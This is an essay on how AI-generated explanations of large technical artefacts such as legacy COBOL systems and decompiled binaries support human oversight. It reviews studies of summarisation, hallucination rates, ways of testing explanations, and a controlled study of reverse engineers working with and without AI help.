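# Using AI to explain complex technical systems to people

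## What it takes to explain a technical artefact, and how an explanation is tested

People are often responsible for technical systems that they cannot read. A bank manager may have to approve a change to a decades-old payments program, or a mathematician may have to decide whether to accept a proof that a machine wrote. Large language models (LLMs), which are AI models trained on text to read and write both language and code, can now describe such programs and proofs in ordinary prose. The *artefact* is the thing that needs explaining, whether a program, a proof, a log or a trained model. The *explainer* is the AI system that produces the explanation.

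The basic difficulty in explaining a technical artefact is its size. A common figure for how fast a person can read code carefully comes from a study at the network equipment maker Cisco that ended in 2006, in which 50 developers carried out 2,500 reviews covering 3.2 million lines. AgileConnection's *The Largest Case Study of Code Reviews—Ever*, a summary by the firm that sold Cisco the review software, puts the sensible limit at 400 to 500 lines an hour and concludes that above 1,000 the reviewer is probably not looking at the code at all. At 400 lines an hour, a million lines take 2,500 hours, more than a year of full-time work, and attention drops after 60 to 90 minutes at a stretch. Even a proper review should find only 70 to 90% of the defects, according to *Best Practices for Code Review* by SmartBear, the same firm. The Cisco developers were reviewing changes to a product they worked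 on, so a stranger to the program would presumably do worse.

### Why explanations should help oversight

*Human oversight* is people's ability to know what a system does, judge it and intervene in time. The case for using AI explanations in oversight starts with the need to know what a system does before approving or stopping it. *Closing the Software Understanding Gap* (2025), which the US Cybersecurity and Infrastructure Security Agency (CISA) wrote with the National Security Agency and two Defense Department bodies, applies this to power grids, weapons and transport. The agencies argue that operators must be able to ask questions about the software and get thorough answers quickly. At present they mostly cannot, and they rely instead on suppliers' assurances, monitoring and lists of components. One of the report's examples is a 2007 flight of twelve F-22 fighters from Hawaii to Japan.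 An on-board computer crashed as the planes crossed the International Date Line, and navigation, fuel and communication systems failed with it. NASA's *Closing the Software Understanding Gap* (2026) describes the same problem in the agency's own missions, where people build software faster than they can understand and verify it.

Checking a claim also often takes much less work than finding it. Suppose an explainer reports that a payments program refuses any withdrawal larger than the balance, and names the function responsible. Finding that rule in a million lines of code might take weeks, but testing it takes one attempted withdrawal on a copy of the system. In a cleaner example from mathematics, multiplying two square tables of numbers with a thousand rows each takes about a billion multiplications by the ordinary method. A checker can test the answer by multiplying both sides of the claimed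 equation by a random column of zeros and ones and comparing the results, which takes about three million steps. A wrong answer passes at most half the time, so it passes five such tests at most once in 32.

Some claims are harder to test. The claim that nothing else in the program can change the balance covers all million lines, so no single run can establish it. Security questions very often have this form.

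The whole argument depends on the reader being able to check the claims without trusting the explainer. Fok (2023), in *In Search of Verifiability*, argues that explanations help a decision-maker only to the extent that they let that person verify the AI's answer, and that in most tasks the answer is not easy to verify, whatever form the explanation takes. Zhang, Foster and Sedoc (2026), in *Human–LLM Deliberation as Interactive Proof*, make the condition exact by counting a check as evidence only if a false claim has a known chance of failing it, however the LLM answers. Asking the explainer whether it is sure does not meet this standard, nor does asking it to elaborate, although the elaboration may show the reader where to look next. An *independent check* is one that does not depend on the explainer's word, such as running the code, looking up the cited line, or passing a proof through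 a proof-checking program.

Lawyers have separately reached a similar rule. *Administrative Law's Fourth Settlement* (2026), on government agencies that use AI to help decide cases, recommends that explanations cite specific evidence, that somebody check the citations against the record, and that claims about what drove a decision be tested against the system's behaviour in similar cases.

People have long worried that commentary makes readers lazy. In about 15% of the Cisco reviews, the programmer had annotated the code beforehand, and the reviewers found hardly any defects. Either the programmers had caught their own mistakes while explaining the code, or the reviewers had stopped thinking and merely matched comments to code. The analysts looked through 300 of these reviews and favoured the first explanation, because reviewers had often argued with the comments. This is reassuring when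 programmers annotate their own code, but it transfers poorly to an LLM describing code it did not write, because writing the description does not lead anyone to repair the code.

### Explaining something longer than the model can read

An LLM can take in only a limited amount of text at once, called its *context window*. This limit is measured in tokens, which are words or pieces of words. At roughly ten tokens a line, a million-line program is about ten million tokens long, but GPT-5, OpenAI's main model of 2025, had a window of 272,000 tokens.

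The standard way round this is to summarise in stages. *BooookScore* (2023), a study of book-length summaries, describes two versions. In hierarchical merging, the LLM summarises each chunk of the text, then merges as many neighbouring summaries as fit in the window, and repeats the merging until one summary remains. In incremental updating, it summarises the first chunk and then revises that summary as it reads each further chunk. For the ten-million-token program, chunks of 8,000 tokens would give 1,250 first summaries. If each merge combined ten of them, the next levels would hold 125, 13, 2 and finally 1, and the model would write the final summary from the two before it, without seeing the code.

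Mistakes in low-level summaries tend to carry over into the summaries built on them. Suppose a function checks withdrawals against the balance, except on accounts with a certain flag. The first summary omits the flag for brevity. At the next level, that summary is combined with nine others and shortened to "the program checks withdrawals". At the top, this becomes "all withdrawals are checked against the balance", which is false. The omission became an error as the statements grew more general, though nothing was invented at any stage.

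Studies only partly agree on how serious a problem errors become when summaries are repeatedly merged. *Context-Aware Hierarchical Merging for Long Document Summarization* (Ou and Lapata, 2025), which used court files and novels of more than 100,000 tokens, starts from the observation that repeated merging can amplify an LLM's fabrications. It got more faithful summaries by bringing back passages of the original at every level, either beside the intermediate summaries or in place of them. *RAPTOR* (2024), on a system that arranges summaries in a tree, found minor fabrications (one made two characters in a novel sisters, without support in the text) but saw none of them spread to higher layers. Both findings can be true because a merge that drops small details will also drop small false ones, leaving the errors that look important. Errors can also harm the next stage more than gaps do. *Reversa*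 (2026), on producing specifications for old software, cites experiments in which incorrect documentation damaged an LLM's understanding of code while missing documentation did not necessarily do so.

A newer approach keeps the text outside the model's context window. The LLM writes small programs to search the text, calls itself on the pieces they return and combines the results. Zhang, Kraska and Khattab (2025) tested this with GPT-5 in *Recursive Language Models*. On multiple-choice questions about code repositories, the model alone scored 24%, partly because some inputs did not fit in the window. Repeated summarising scored 58%, and the recursive method scored 62 to 66% at its two best-performing settings, a modest gain over summarising. On a synthetic task that required comparing nearly every pair of entries in a list, summarising scored 0.1 and the recursive method 58 or more. The second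 result matters for explaining programs because the dangerous fault is often a conflict between two distant pieces of code that look unremarkable when summarised separately.

### Faithful, plausible, confabulated

In *Enhancing Understanding of Language Models with Varied Explanations*, Sun (2026) distinguishes how closely an explanation reflects the underlying computation from how coherent and understandable people find it. The distinction applies to any artefact. A *faithful* explanation accurately states what the artefact does and why. A *plausible* explanation convinces a reader, whether or not it is faithful. Readers can judge plausibility from the explanation alone, which is why people so easily substitute it for faithfulness.

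A *confabulation* is a specific, fluent claim that nothing in the artefact supports, such as a description of a safety check that no line of the code performs. Most work on LLMs uses the broader word "hallucination". *Refusing the Impossible* (2026), a benchmark of code hallucination, found that two thirds of the hallucinations contained no hedging. The wording of the request mattered more than the choice of model. When a request looked like routine internal documentation, models fabricated at a rate of 0.64, compared with 0.44 for a casual question. This matters because much of what people want explainers to write is documentation.

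Reported error rates vary widely, partly because researchers count different things. In *RubberDuckBench* (2026), a set of questions about code, 58.3% of answers on average contained at least one hallucination. Korn, Bartel and colleagues (2026), in *On the Viability of Requirements Generation From Code*, counted individual claims. They had an LLM read two programs of 24,000 and 28,000 lines and write down what each program is required to do, and human evaluators then judged whether the code did it. Seven of the 114 statements (6.1%) were false. The rate was 1.8% for a well-maintained open-source program and 10.3% for a student project. The two studies' results are closer than they look, because an answer that makes fourteen claims, each with a 6% chance of being false, has a 58% chance of containing at least one false claim. The 6.1% figure is also somewhat uncertain. Another LLM agent chose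 the code excerpts that the evaluators worked from, so their check was not fully independent.

*Comprehension* is what the reader can correctly state, predict or do after reading, as measured by a test. *Overreliance* is the reader's acceptance of an AI's statement when it is wrong. Jain, Bridgers and colleagues (2025) observed overreliance in *Human-AI Complementarity* when they showed fact-checkers an AI's explanation, confidence and verdict together.

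### Four ways to test an explanation

The simplest test is to ask experts to rate the explanation, which is quick and needs no access to a running system. But raters disagree. Korn and colleagues had experienced evaluators score each generated statement from 1 to 5 for proper form and for whether it described behaviour one could expect from such a program. Two evaluators gave the same score 36% of the time, and their agreement was 0.178, where 0 is chance and 1 is perfect. Asking whether behaviour could be expected also tests only whether it is plausible. An expert who has not read the artefact can judge little else, and has no way to notice what the explanation leaves out.

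Prediction is a harder test. If an explanation is faithful, someone who has read it should be better at foretelling what the artefact will do with new inputs, and running the artefact supplies the answers. Mayne, Kang and colleagues (2026), in *A Positive Case for Faithfulness*, applied this to LLMs that explain their own decisions, a case in which artefact and explainer are the same. A model judged, for instance, whether a patient had heart disease, and explained its answer. Five other LLMs then predicted its verdict on a similar patient, once without the explanation and once with it. The score is the share of the possible improvement that the explanation delivers:

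(accuracy with explanation − accuracy without) ÷ (1 − accuracy without)

If predictors are right 70% of the time without the explanation and 79% with it, they have gained 9 of the 30 percentage points available, a score of 0.3. Across 18 models and 7,000 pairs of cases, the scores ran from 0.11 to 0.37, so the explanations helped but left most of the possible improvement unrealised. Between 5 and 15% of the explanations were highly misleading, meaning that all five predictors got the new case wrong. In one example, GPT-5.2 had to choose between driving straight on, which would kill four men, and swerving, which would kill four women. It chose to drive on, citing the principle that it should not take active measures, but chose to swerve when the sexes were exchanged.

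A prediction test can mislead if its cases are poorly chosen. Hong and Roth ran such a test with human participants and LLM judges in *Do LLM Self-Explanations Help Users Predict Model Behavior?* (2026). Explanations helped both groups, but the size of the gain depended strongly on how the researchers had varied the questions. It also depended on the judge. A weaker LLM gained about 30 percentage points on average and a stronger one about 15, because the stronger one already predicted well without explanations. Good predictions on ordinary inputs are also no evidence about rare ones. An explanation of the F-22 software that missed the date line fault could have passed thousands of tests on flights that never crossed the line.

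In an intervention test, someone changes the artefact and checks for the predicted effect. If the explanation is that a certain function enforces the withdrawal limit, an engineer can disable that function in a copy and try to overdraw an account. This tests why the limit holds, which a prediction test does not. Madsen, Ismail and colleagues (2026), in *Scaling Inherently Interpretable Language Models*, point out that a neural network may make no use of information that researchers can read off its internal state. Researchers get better evidence of use by amplifying or suppressing the information and watching the output, and they test automatic labels for a model's neurons in much the same way.

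Intervention can still make a true explanation look false, because large systems contain redundant parts. Disabling the function may change nothing if a second one does the same job. Intervention can also make a false explanation look true. *The Dead Salmons of AI Interpretability* (2025) collects cases in which common methods for explaining neural networks, including causal ones, gave plausible accounts of networks with random connections, which had learned nothing. Its title refers to a 2009 experiment in which standard brain-scan analysis found signs of social emotion in a dead fish. The paper also describes small networks for which several incompatible explanations fit equally well. It proposes applying the same method to a randomised copy of the network as a control, and discounting any findings that also appear there.

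An explanation can pass all three tests so far even if nobody understands it. A comprehension test uses questions about the artefact to compare people who have read the explanation with people who have not. The answer key must come from the artefact, because a key based on the explanation would reward readers for learning its mistakes. Asking readers whether they understand is not a substitute. In *Overseeing Agents Without Constant Oversight* (Grunde-McLaughlin, Mozannar and colleagues, 2026), people who reviewed the work of AI agents with a new interface found errors faster and felt more confident, but their accuracy did not meaningfully improve. However, a comprehension test covers only what somebody thought to ask, and a low score does not show whether the explanation was false or just hard to follow.

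### How much a spot check can find

In practice, the reader will check part of a long explanation. If an explanation makes 200 claims and each is 98% likely to be true, about four will be false. The better of Korn and colleagues' two programs had a similar error rate. If the errors are independent, the chance that all 200 claims are true is under 2%.

Suppose exactly four are false and the reader checks 20 claims at random, never the same one twice. The chance that all 20 are true is

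(180 × 179 × 178 × 177) ÷ (200 × 199 × 198 × 197) ≈ 0.65

so the reader finds at least one false claim with a chance of about 35%. For a 95% chance the reader would have to check 105 claims, more than half of the explanation.

Often only one of the four false claims matters. Three may get a date or a file name wrong, while the last states that the program checks all withdrawals. A reader who checks 20 of the 200 claims has a 10% chance of including that last one, and would need to check 190 for a 95% chance. If the explanation had 12 false claims, roughly the 6.1% rate, the reader would have about a 73% chance of finding at least one and learning that the text is unreliable, but the chance of checking the dangerous claim would still be 10%.

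These figures assume that the reader checks without error. In the interactive-proof model of Zhang and colleagues, the chance of catching a false claim is proportional to the reader's reliability, so someone who does nine checks in ten correctly has a 9% chance of catching the dangerous claim. They also show that many small checks can work better than one large one, because a person with limited time may compare two entries reliably but fail to verify a long argument in one pass. However, each extra check is another chance to reject a true claim by mistake.

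Choosing which claims to check helps more than checking a few more. If 30 of the 200 claims concern money or safety and the reader uses all 20 checks on those, the chance of checking the dangerous one rises to two in three, provided it looks dangerous. It may not, so Zhang and colleagues keep a fixed share of the checks random and let the reader choose the rest by suspicion.

Checking the 200 claims, whether a sample or all of them, will not reveal what the explainer left out. In an example from Zhang and colleagues, an organiser reviews a conference timetable that an LLM has drawn up. Before starting the conversation with the LLM, the organiser uses the timetable itself to write a list of things to verify. This takes an hour for a timetable, but writing such a list for a million lines of code already requires much of the understanding that the explanation was supposed to supply.

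## Old business and government programs that few people can still read

Many banks and government agencies depend on decades-old programs in languages that few programmers now learn. In *Information Technology* (2025), the US Government Accountability Office (GAO), which audits federal agencies for Congress, identified 11 of the most critical old systems in the federal government. MeriTalk, a news site on government technology, reported that they are 23 to 60 years old and that seven run with known security weaknesses. Both of the Treasury systems on the list use COBOL, a business language from 1959, and assembly language, in which each line is typically one small instruction to the processor. GAO found that fewer and fewer people have the skills to support them. The Social Security Administration once had to rehire retired developers to maintain a COBOL application, DevX reported in *Report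 Calls Out U.S. Government for Aging Technology*. *Enhancing COBOL Code Explanations* (Lei, Zou and colleagues, 2025) cites estimates that COBOL handles 80% of financial service transactions and 95% of ATM swipes.

COBOL resembles English, and a line such as PERFORM VALIDATE-SALARY is easy to read, but a whole program is harder to read because it is long. Lei and colleagues cite an average of 600 lines per COBOL program, where Java would need 30 or fewer. Programmers also define the data in one part of a file, or in a separate file that a COPY statement pulls in, and use it somewhere else. Experts who reviewed artificial COBOL for *Spec2COBOLRot* (2026) found it too clean to pass for industrial code, partly because it had no COPY statements and closed every IF block explicitly. In real programs an IF often ends at the next full stop, so one misplaced full stop changes which instructions depend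 on the condition.

MUMPS, a language and database from the 1960s for managing medical records, is terser. *Leveraging LLMs for Legacy Code Modernization* (Diggs, Doyle and colleagues, 2024) reports that MUMPS programmers may put five or six statements on a line. The US Veterans Health Administration's record system, VistA, has more than 36,000 files of MUMPS code.

Programs in all these languages contain business rules that often aren't written down anywhere else. MITRE, a nonprofit that does research for US agencies, points out that the federal government's old software contains decades of laws and regulations. To check whether a program still follows the law, an official may have to piece one rule together from conditions, lookup tables and shared data definitions in several programs, and the people who wrote them have often retired.

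### How two models explain a COBOL project

Lei and colleagues, from Queen's University in Canada and IBM, built a COBOL explainer from two LLMs, which they call agents. The Code Processing Agent is IBM's Granite, a model trained on code that can take in 8,192 tokens at once. It reads the COBOL and describes it. The Text Processing Agent is OpenAI's GPT-4o mini, which can take in 128,000 tokens. It works from Granite's descriptions, not the code, and merges them into longer ones. Both models are weak by the standards of late 2026, so the method is more interesting than the absolute scores.

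The system starts with functions, which are named blocks of code that other parts of the program can run. COBOL calls them paragraphs. The system extracts the names of the function's variables and of any other functions it calls, and adds them to the prompt with the code. Granite then describes the function in about 75 words. When the limit was 50 words or less, the model tended to stop before finishing, and when it was above 100, the model repeated itself.

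Such a description may mention that the function runs 1000-PROCESS-SALES without explaining what that does. Gaps like this are a known source of false statements. *Identifying Inaccurate Descriptions in LLM-generated Code Comments via Test Execution* (2024) reports that one typical error of an earlier model was to misdescribe behaviour that comes from called code it could not see. Lei and colleagues fill the gap by working from the bottom up. A function that calls nothing keeps its description. Once all the functions that another function calls have final descriptions, GPT-4o mini rewrites the caller's description to include theirs.

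In Lei and colleagues' sample program, a main section runs three functions. One sets a counter to zero, another adds to it, and the third, VALIDATE-SALARY, passes an employee's salary to another program, CheckSalary, and displays whether the salary is valid. The system would describe these three functions and then the main section. But the rules for a valid salary are in CheckSalary, a separate file, so they would be covered only at the project level. The procedure also assumes that calls form a hierarchy. It counts GO TO as a call, and old COBOL often uses GO TO to jump back to an earlier paragraph. If two functions jumped to each other, neither could get a final description before the other, unless some further rule broke the loop.

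For a file that fits in Granite's context window, the prompt contains the code, the variables, the file name and the program's identifier, because names often hint at the business purpose. For a longer file, GPT-4o mini merges the function descriptions in stages, using a list of which function calls which. It builds the project explanation in the same way from the file descriptions and a ranking of the files, from those that no other file calls down to those that call no others. If an early summary leaves out an exception, GPT-4o mini can't recover it because it doesn't have the code.

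### Closer to the programmers' words

The baseline for functions was Granite given only the code. Lei and colleagues scored both versions against comments by the original programmers. They extracted 2,316 functions from 14 open-source projects but kept only the 243 with comments that two of them agreed were correct, so the test covers only the best-documented tenth of the functions.

The extra context moved the wording closer to the programmers' own, with no detectable change in how closely the meaning matched. METEOR, which counts matching words and allows for synonyms, rose from 0.134 to 0.151, and chrF, which compares short runs of letters, rose from 0.199 to 0.236. The score on SentenceBERT, which uses a language model to compare meanings, went from 0.405 to 0.407, a change that was not statistically significant.

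Lei and colleagues treat high similarity between an explanation and the programmer's comment as a sign that the explanation is not hallucinated. But a wrong explanation can also closely resemble the comment. For example, "checks the withdrawal against the balance" and "never checks the withdrawal against the balance" share almost all their words. An explanation can also score lower for including a true statement that the programmer left out of the comment.

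GPT-4o also scored the explanations, again with the programmers' comments as the benchmark. It gave the function explanations an average of 6.01 out of 10, against 5.57 for the baseline. For files, the scores were 6.68 against 6.41 for purpose, 6.30 against 5.69 for functionality and 6.64 against 5.79 for clarity. This comparison covers only files short enough for the baseline to process, not the long files where the method is most needed.

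In the only test of accuracy, two of the authors judged by hand whether 54 of the function explanations described the code correctly. The mean score was 0.995 out of 1, which is very good, but the judges had built the system and the functions all had good comments. The same explanations covered about 77% of what the programmers' comments contained, so omissions were much more common than false statements.

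In the study, 10 of 11 project-level explanations covered the functions described in the project's README file, the introduction that developers write for newcomers. The exception was zECS, which its developers describe as a distributed caching service, one that keeps data ready for other programs to fetch. The explanation correctly described the files as handling web requests but missed the caching, because that use of the system is not evident from the code. More context from the codebase would not have helped, so somebody has to supply the purpose from outside it.

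### Whether a score can replace an expert

Diggs and colleagues, at MITRE, had already looked in 2024 for an automatic measure that would spare organisations the cost of expert review. They took 78 MUMPS files from VistA and 12 files of IBM mainframe assembly that Walmart had published, replaced the programmers' comments with placeholders, and had four LLMs of the time write new ones. Four MUMPS experts and five mainframe experts rated a sample of these and of the original comments from 1 to 4 on each part of a rubric:

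- hallucination: whether the comment is true
- readability: whether it is clearly written
- completeness: whether it covers everything essential that the code does
- usefulness: whether it helps a programmer understand the code, with the top mark for helping an expert

With ratings converted to a 10-point scale, GPT-4's comments on MUMPS code averaged 9.1 for truth. On assembly code, Llama 3's comments averaged 6.53 and the programmers' own comments only 7.31. But the mainframe experts who rated the assembly comments hardly agreed with one another. On a scale where 1 is perfect agreement, they scored 0.22 on truth and 0.12 on usefulness, while the MUMPS experts scored 0.73 on truth. The assembly ratings therefore show little except that experienced people differ about what makes a good comment.

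None of the automatic measures correlated well with the ratings. The strongest correlation with comment quality was 0.34, between usefulness and similarity in meaning to the original comment, which accounts for about 12% of the variation. ChrF, one of the scores Lei and colleagues later relied on, correlated with truth at 0.06 on MUMPS and 0.24 on assembly.

A follow-up, *Can LLMs Replace Humans During Code Chunking?* (Glasz, Escamilla and colleagues, 2025), used LLMs to rate the comments instead. This took 1.28 million requests to GPT-4o and cost $8,547. GPT-4o's repeated scores for the same comment agreed at 0.91 or better, far above the mainframe experts' agreement. But consistent scores can still be wrong, since a model can repeat the same mistake. Glasz and colleagues report that comments were up to 20% more factual when an LLM rather than a person decided where to split the code, but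 no human checked the comments, so this shows only that the LLM judge scored them higher.

In *Ensemble Methodology for Reference-Free Confidence Estimation in LLM-based Code Summarization*, Colombo, Tokkar and colleagues (2026) did use experts. People with at least 15 years of mainframe experience wrote their own summaries of code from a credit card program that Amazon publishes as a demonstration, and reviewers compared an LLM's summaries with these. Colombo and colleagues describe a sample of 100 pieces of code but give results for 30. The reviewers accepted 22 summaries and judged that 8 needed further review or rejection. Omissions were again the main problem. Three summaries left out the handling of file errors, three left out branches for unusual cases, and two described the validation of data incompletely. In one case the LLM wrote that a paragraph of code generates reports, but left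 out that there are three different reports, each with its own selection criteria, which are the kind of business rule a maintainer is looking for.

The goal of the study was to develop a confidence score that could identify summaries good enough to use without human review. The experts accepted 16 of the 17 summaries with high scores. The sample is tiny, but if that rate held, about 590 of every 10,000 high-scoring summaries used without review would be faulty.

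### What "three times faster" means

*Leveraging Generative AI for Extracting Business Requirements from Legacy COBOL and PL/I* (Kalohia, 2026) reports the largest of these studies, on 3.4 million lines from a financial company. Kalohia has an interest in the result, since *Using GenAI for Extracting Business Requirements from Legacy COBOL Code and PL/I* (Kalohia and Liubushak, 2025) presents such a tool as a platform of the software company EPAM. The tool can also read PL/I, another old mainframe language, but the test corpus contained only COBOL and job-control scripts.

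Conventional software first breaks the code into its grammatical parts and traces how control and data move through the program. An OpenAI model then uses these facts to fill in a fixed form with sections such as purpose, inputs, business rules and exceptions. Another program checks that every paragraph and data item the model cites exists in the code, and links each rule to the lines of code that support it. Analysts accept or edit the result. In informal trials, the LLM hallucinated more and had weaker coverage when used alone.

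| Kind of program | Lines | Hours, manual | Hours, tool | Errors, manual | Errors, tool |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Online COBOL | 1,700,000 | 5,440 | 1,630 | 2,230 | 2,398 |
| Batch COBOL | 1,100,000 | 3,520 | 1,100 | 1,789 | 1,935 |
| CICS (live transactions) | 480,000 | 1,536 | 470 | 898 | 1,022 |
| JCL (job-control scripts) | 122,000 | 390 | 120 | 575 | 595 |

The tool was 3.2 to 3.3 times faster than manual analysis, which covered about 313 lines an hour. For three of the four kinds of program, the manual pace is exactly 312.5 lines an hour, or 2,500 lines in an eight-hour day. Analysts are unlikely to have kept exactly the same pace on such different code, so the baseline is probably a planning estimate rather than a measurement.

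Analysts using the tool cover about 1,000 lines an hour, roughly the pace at which the Cisco reviewers seemed to stop looking at the code. Kalohia designed the workflow so that analysts read as little of the source as possible. They check the explanation instead, and can follow links into the code when they want to.

The tool also made about 8% more errors than the manual analysis, 5,950 against 5,492. Many organisations would accept that to save 70% of the hours, if the errors were of the same kind. Kalohia does not break the errors down by severity, but lists missing rules among the typical failures. The headline accuracy figure of 93% leaves out missing rules. The body of the paper gives it as precision, meaning that 93% of the extracted rules that two experts sampled were correct. Kalohia also lists recall, the share of all the rules in the code that the tool found, as a planned measure,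 but the results include no figure for it. The links do not help reviewers find missing rules either, since a rule that the tool missed has no link.

### When the old comments are wrong

An AI that explains old code usually reads the old comments too. These can be false, because programmers often fix a bug without updating the comment beside it. Sabetto, Escamilla and colleagues (2025), in *Impact of Comments on LLM Comprehension of Legacy Code*, tested how comments affected four LLMs' understanding of L8WAIT, a module of Walmart's assembly code that sets a waiting time. The models took multiple-choice quizzes that the researchers wrote with two assembly experts, so the answer key came from the code and the experts rather than from a reference text.

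Accurate comments helped the models, whose average score on the harder quiz rose from 84% with the code alone to 90% with all its comments. The models still scored 75% without any code, so they had probably seen the module in training, which makes it hard to judge how much either the code or the comments helped.

Sabetto and colleagues tested false comments by first replacing a fifth of the originals with instructions for working out a waiter's tip, which had almost no effect. They then replaced all of them with the description of a basketball simulation, and the average score on ten questions about the code fell to 61%, from 73% with the true comments. When asked what the module does, GPT-4 relied on the false comments and called it "a comprehensive simulation tool for predicting the outcome of an NBA season". The models did not check for a mismatch unprompted, but they could often detect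 one when asked. They got 84% right on questions that pointed them to particular comments and asked about their accuracy.

These models are at least two generations old, and one module with ten questions is weak evidence. Real comments are also wrong in less absurd ways. An outdated comment describes what the code used to do, so it is more plausible than a comment about basketball and harder to notice. Even specialists can describe a program inaccurately. Lei and colleagues caption their sample as one that accumulates an employee's salary, but no line of it adds anything to the salary.

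More recent work suggests that the kind of error matters. In *Talking to Itself While Coding* (2026), which studies LLMs writing code rather than explaining it, correct comments raised the success rate by 17.2% and comments about a different problem lowered it by 20.8%. Comments that described a wrong solution to the right problem made no difference. The earlier studies reviewed in *Inside Out* (2025) are also mixed. One found that incorrect comments do substantial damage, and another that LLMs summarise code more accurately with the comments removed. A team that does not know how good its comments are could generate each explanation twice, with and without the comments, and have somebody check the code wherever the two versions disagree.

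### What maintainers could do afterwards

None of the studies of old code measured comprehension in people. Sabetto and colleagues quizzed the models, Diggs and colleagues asked experts for their opinion on whether a comment would help a programmer, and Kalohia reports that business analysts gave positive feedback on how readable the documents were. No study gave maintainers an unfamiliar program and compared how well they did with and without an explanation. The nearest result is from *A Study on How Free Use of LLMs Assists Novices with Code Comprehension Tasks* (Sajib, Tamang and colleagues, 2026), which found that introductory students with access to an LLM did better on comprehension tasks and became more confident. Those students worked with the small programs of a first course.

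Banks have begun using AI to explain old code without waiting for such a test. In January 2025 Morgan Stanley introduced DevGen.AI, a tool it had built on OpenAI's models to turn COBOL and other old code into plain-English specifications that developers use to write a modern version. Mike Pizzi, the bank's head of technology, told the Wall Street Journal that by June the tool had reviewed nine million lines of code and saved 280,000 hours (Bousquette, 2025, *How Morgan Stanley Tackled One of Coding's Toughest Problems*). By February 2026 the bank had used it to modernise about 16 million lines, according to American Banker's *Morgan Stanley's Tech Chief Used AI to Crack a Major Coding Problem*.

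Morgan Stanley counted the saved hours itself, and its total is hard to reconcile with Kalohia's figures. At Kalohia's rate of 313 lines an hour, analysing nine million lines by hand would take about 29,000 hours, a tenth of what the bank says it saved. The bank may also be counting the rewriting, or assuming a much slower manual pace. Neither report includes an error rate for the specifications.

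A bank is in a good position to test how well an English specification explains an old program, because the program still runs and the bank has records of the transactions it processed. The bank could give maintainers the specification, ask them what the program did with a few hundred past transactions, including some rare ones, and compare their answers with the records.

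## Compiled programs: a study of reverse engineers with and without AI help

The maintainer of an old COBOL program can read its source code, the code its programmers wrote, but vendors of most commercial software keep the source code private and distribute only the compiled program, a set of instructions for a processor. *Compilation*, the translation of source code into those instructions, discards what the processor does not need, including the comments, most of the names, and most of the information about types, such as whether a number is a price or a location in memory. Compilers also rearrange the code to make it run faster. Kohli, Lee and colleagues (2026) point out in *SoK: Are LLMs Reliable at Source Code Recovery?* that different source programs can produce the same instructions, so nobody can recover the original with certainty.

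Suppose the source code of a payments program contains the line `if (amount > account->balance) return DENIED;` and a comment about the bank's overdraft rules. A *decompiler*, a tool that turns a compiled program back into code resembling what a programmer wrote, might produce `if (a2 > *(_DWORD *)(a1 + 40)) return 3;`. This preserves the comparison and its consequence, but not the names or the reason for the rule. A reader has to work out that `a2` is an amount of money and that the number stored 40 bytes into `a1` is a balance. This work is called *reverse engineering*. It is slow and requires knowledge of processors, compilers and operating systems, as Hu, Fu and colleagues (2026) note in *Potential and Challenges of Large Language Models for Reverse Engineering*.

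The two most widely used decompilers are Hex-Rays, which comes with the commercial tool IDA Pro, and Ghidra, which the US National Security Agency publishes. Both make mistakes. *A Memorization Floor for LLM Refinement of Decompiled Code* (2026) cites a 2024 study that found errors in 4,515 of about 93,000 functions that Ghidra decompiled, or roughly one in twenty.

Defenders have to read compiled programs because criminals do not publish the source code of their malware. *SoK: AI-Augmented Binary Reversing* (2026), a review of 246 papers, also mentions reading them to find vulnerabilities, assess risks from suppliers, and check that a patch fixes what it should. Power grid operators, too, often have only the compiled program.

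### 48 people and two programs

No study of old business code tested whether an explanation helps a person understand an unfamiliar program. Basque, Doria and colleagues (2026) tested this with compiled programs in *Decompiling the Synergy*. They first surveyed 153 practitioners who had used LLMs for reverse engineering, of whom 32% used one often or always. Two thirds called LLMs occasionally beneficial, a quarter called them highly advantageous and 7% found them unhelpful. The most common use, reported by 64%, was summarizing a function. Respondents complained of generic or misleading answers and said that LLMs did worse on code that was large, deliberately obscured or heavily mathematical.

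For the experiment, the researchers recruited 24 self-described novices and 24 self-described experts, who had on average two and six years of experience. Each participant worked on two small programs in the style of hacking competitions and had to explain in writing how an attacker could read a secret file. Each program had 26 functions and fewer than 470 lines of source code, which the participants did not see:

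- *RPC* is a server that lets remote users manipulate a small block of memory. Only the administrator may load the secret file into it, but the program derives a supposedly random value from the clock, so an attacker can guess it.
- *Secrets* is an encrypted file manager. An attacker can trick its display command into showing data derived from the administrator's password. The encryption key depends on only two bytes, which leaves 65,536 possibilities to try.

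Participants analysed two programs using IDA Pro in a browser and could not run them. Each participant had AI help in IDA for one of the two programs, chosen at random, so differences in skill between participants should largely cancel out. They could right-click on a function to have the AI summarise it, rename it or its variables, identify a known algorithm, look for vulnerabilities or document a library function, and they could ask anything else in a chat box. The study ran in 2024 and 2025 with models of that time, including GPT-4o (the default), Claude 3.5 Sonnet and Gemini Pro.

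Two researchers independently scored each write-up from 0 to 8. They gave up to seven points for particular facts about the program, such as the weakness of the key, and an eighth for a fully correct solution. This made the scoring a test of comprehension, with the correct answers taken from the program itself. The scorers agreed on 753 of 768 points. The participants spent 109 hours on the programs and made 1,517 requests to the AI, 625 of them for summaries.

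### Why novices gained and experts did not

The study's main measure is the *understanding rate*, the score divided by the minutes spent. Novices averaged 0.04 points per minute without the AI and 0.07 with it. Over a typical session of 70 minutes, those rates would give about 3 points and 5 points. Basque and colleagues report the improvement as 98.55%, presumably calculated from unrounded figures. The experts' average rose only slightly, and the change was not statistically significant.

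Basque and colleagues conclude that the AI brought novices up to the experts' level, because they found no significant difference between the rates of AI-assisted novices and experts. But Doria, De Rosa and colleagues (2026) note in *Humans vs. Machines*, a follow-up with some of the same researchers, that a test for differences cannot show that two groups are the same. With 24 people in each group, the test could easily miss a moderate gap. Novices were also nine of the ten participants with the lowest rates when using the AI, and five of the ten with the highest, so many of them evidently did not catch up.

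The rate can rise because people understand more or because they reach the same understanding sooner. The difference matters to anyone who has to approve a program, since someone who understands it quickly but shallowly may miss the dangerous part. The scoring may also have favoured the AI. Five of the fourteen factual checkpoints across both programs gave a point for naming a standard algorithm, which LLMs do well. A novice could earn those points by copying the name from a summary.

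Basque and colleagues also make a small error in the comparison they use to show that the experts were better. They report average scores of 4.79 for experts and 3.12 for novices as scores without AI, but these figures match the averages in their table for all sessions, including those with AI. The error does not affect the comparison of novices with and without AI.

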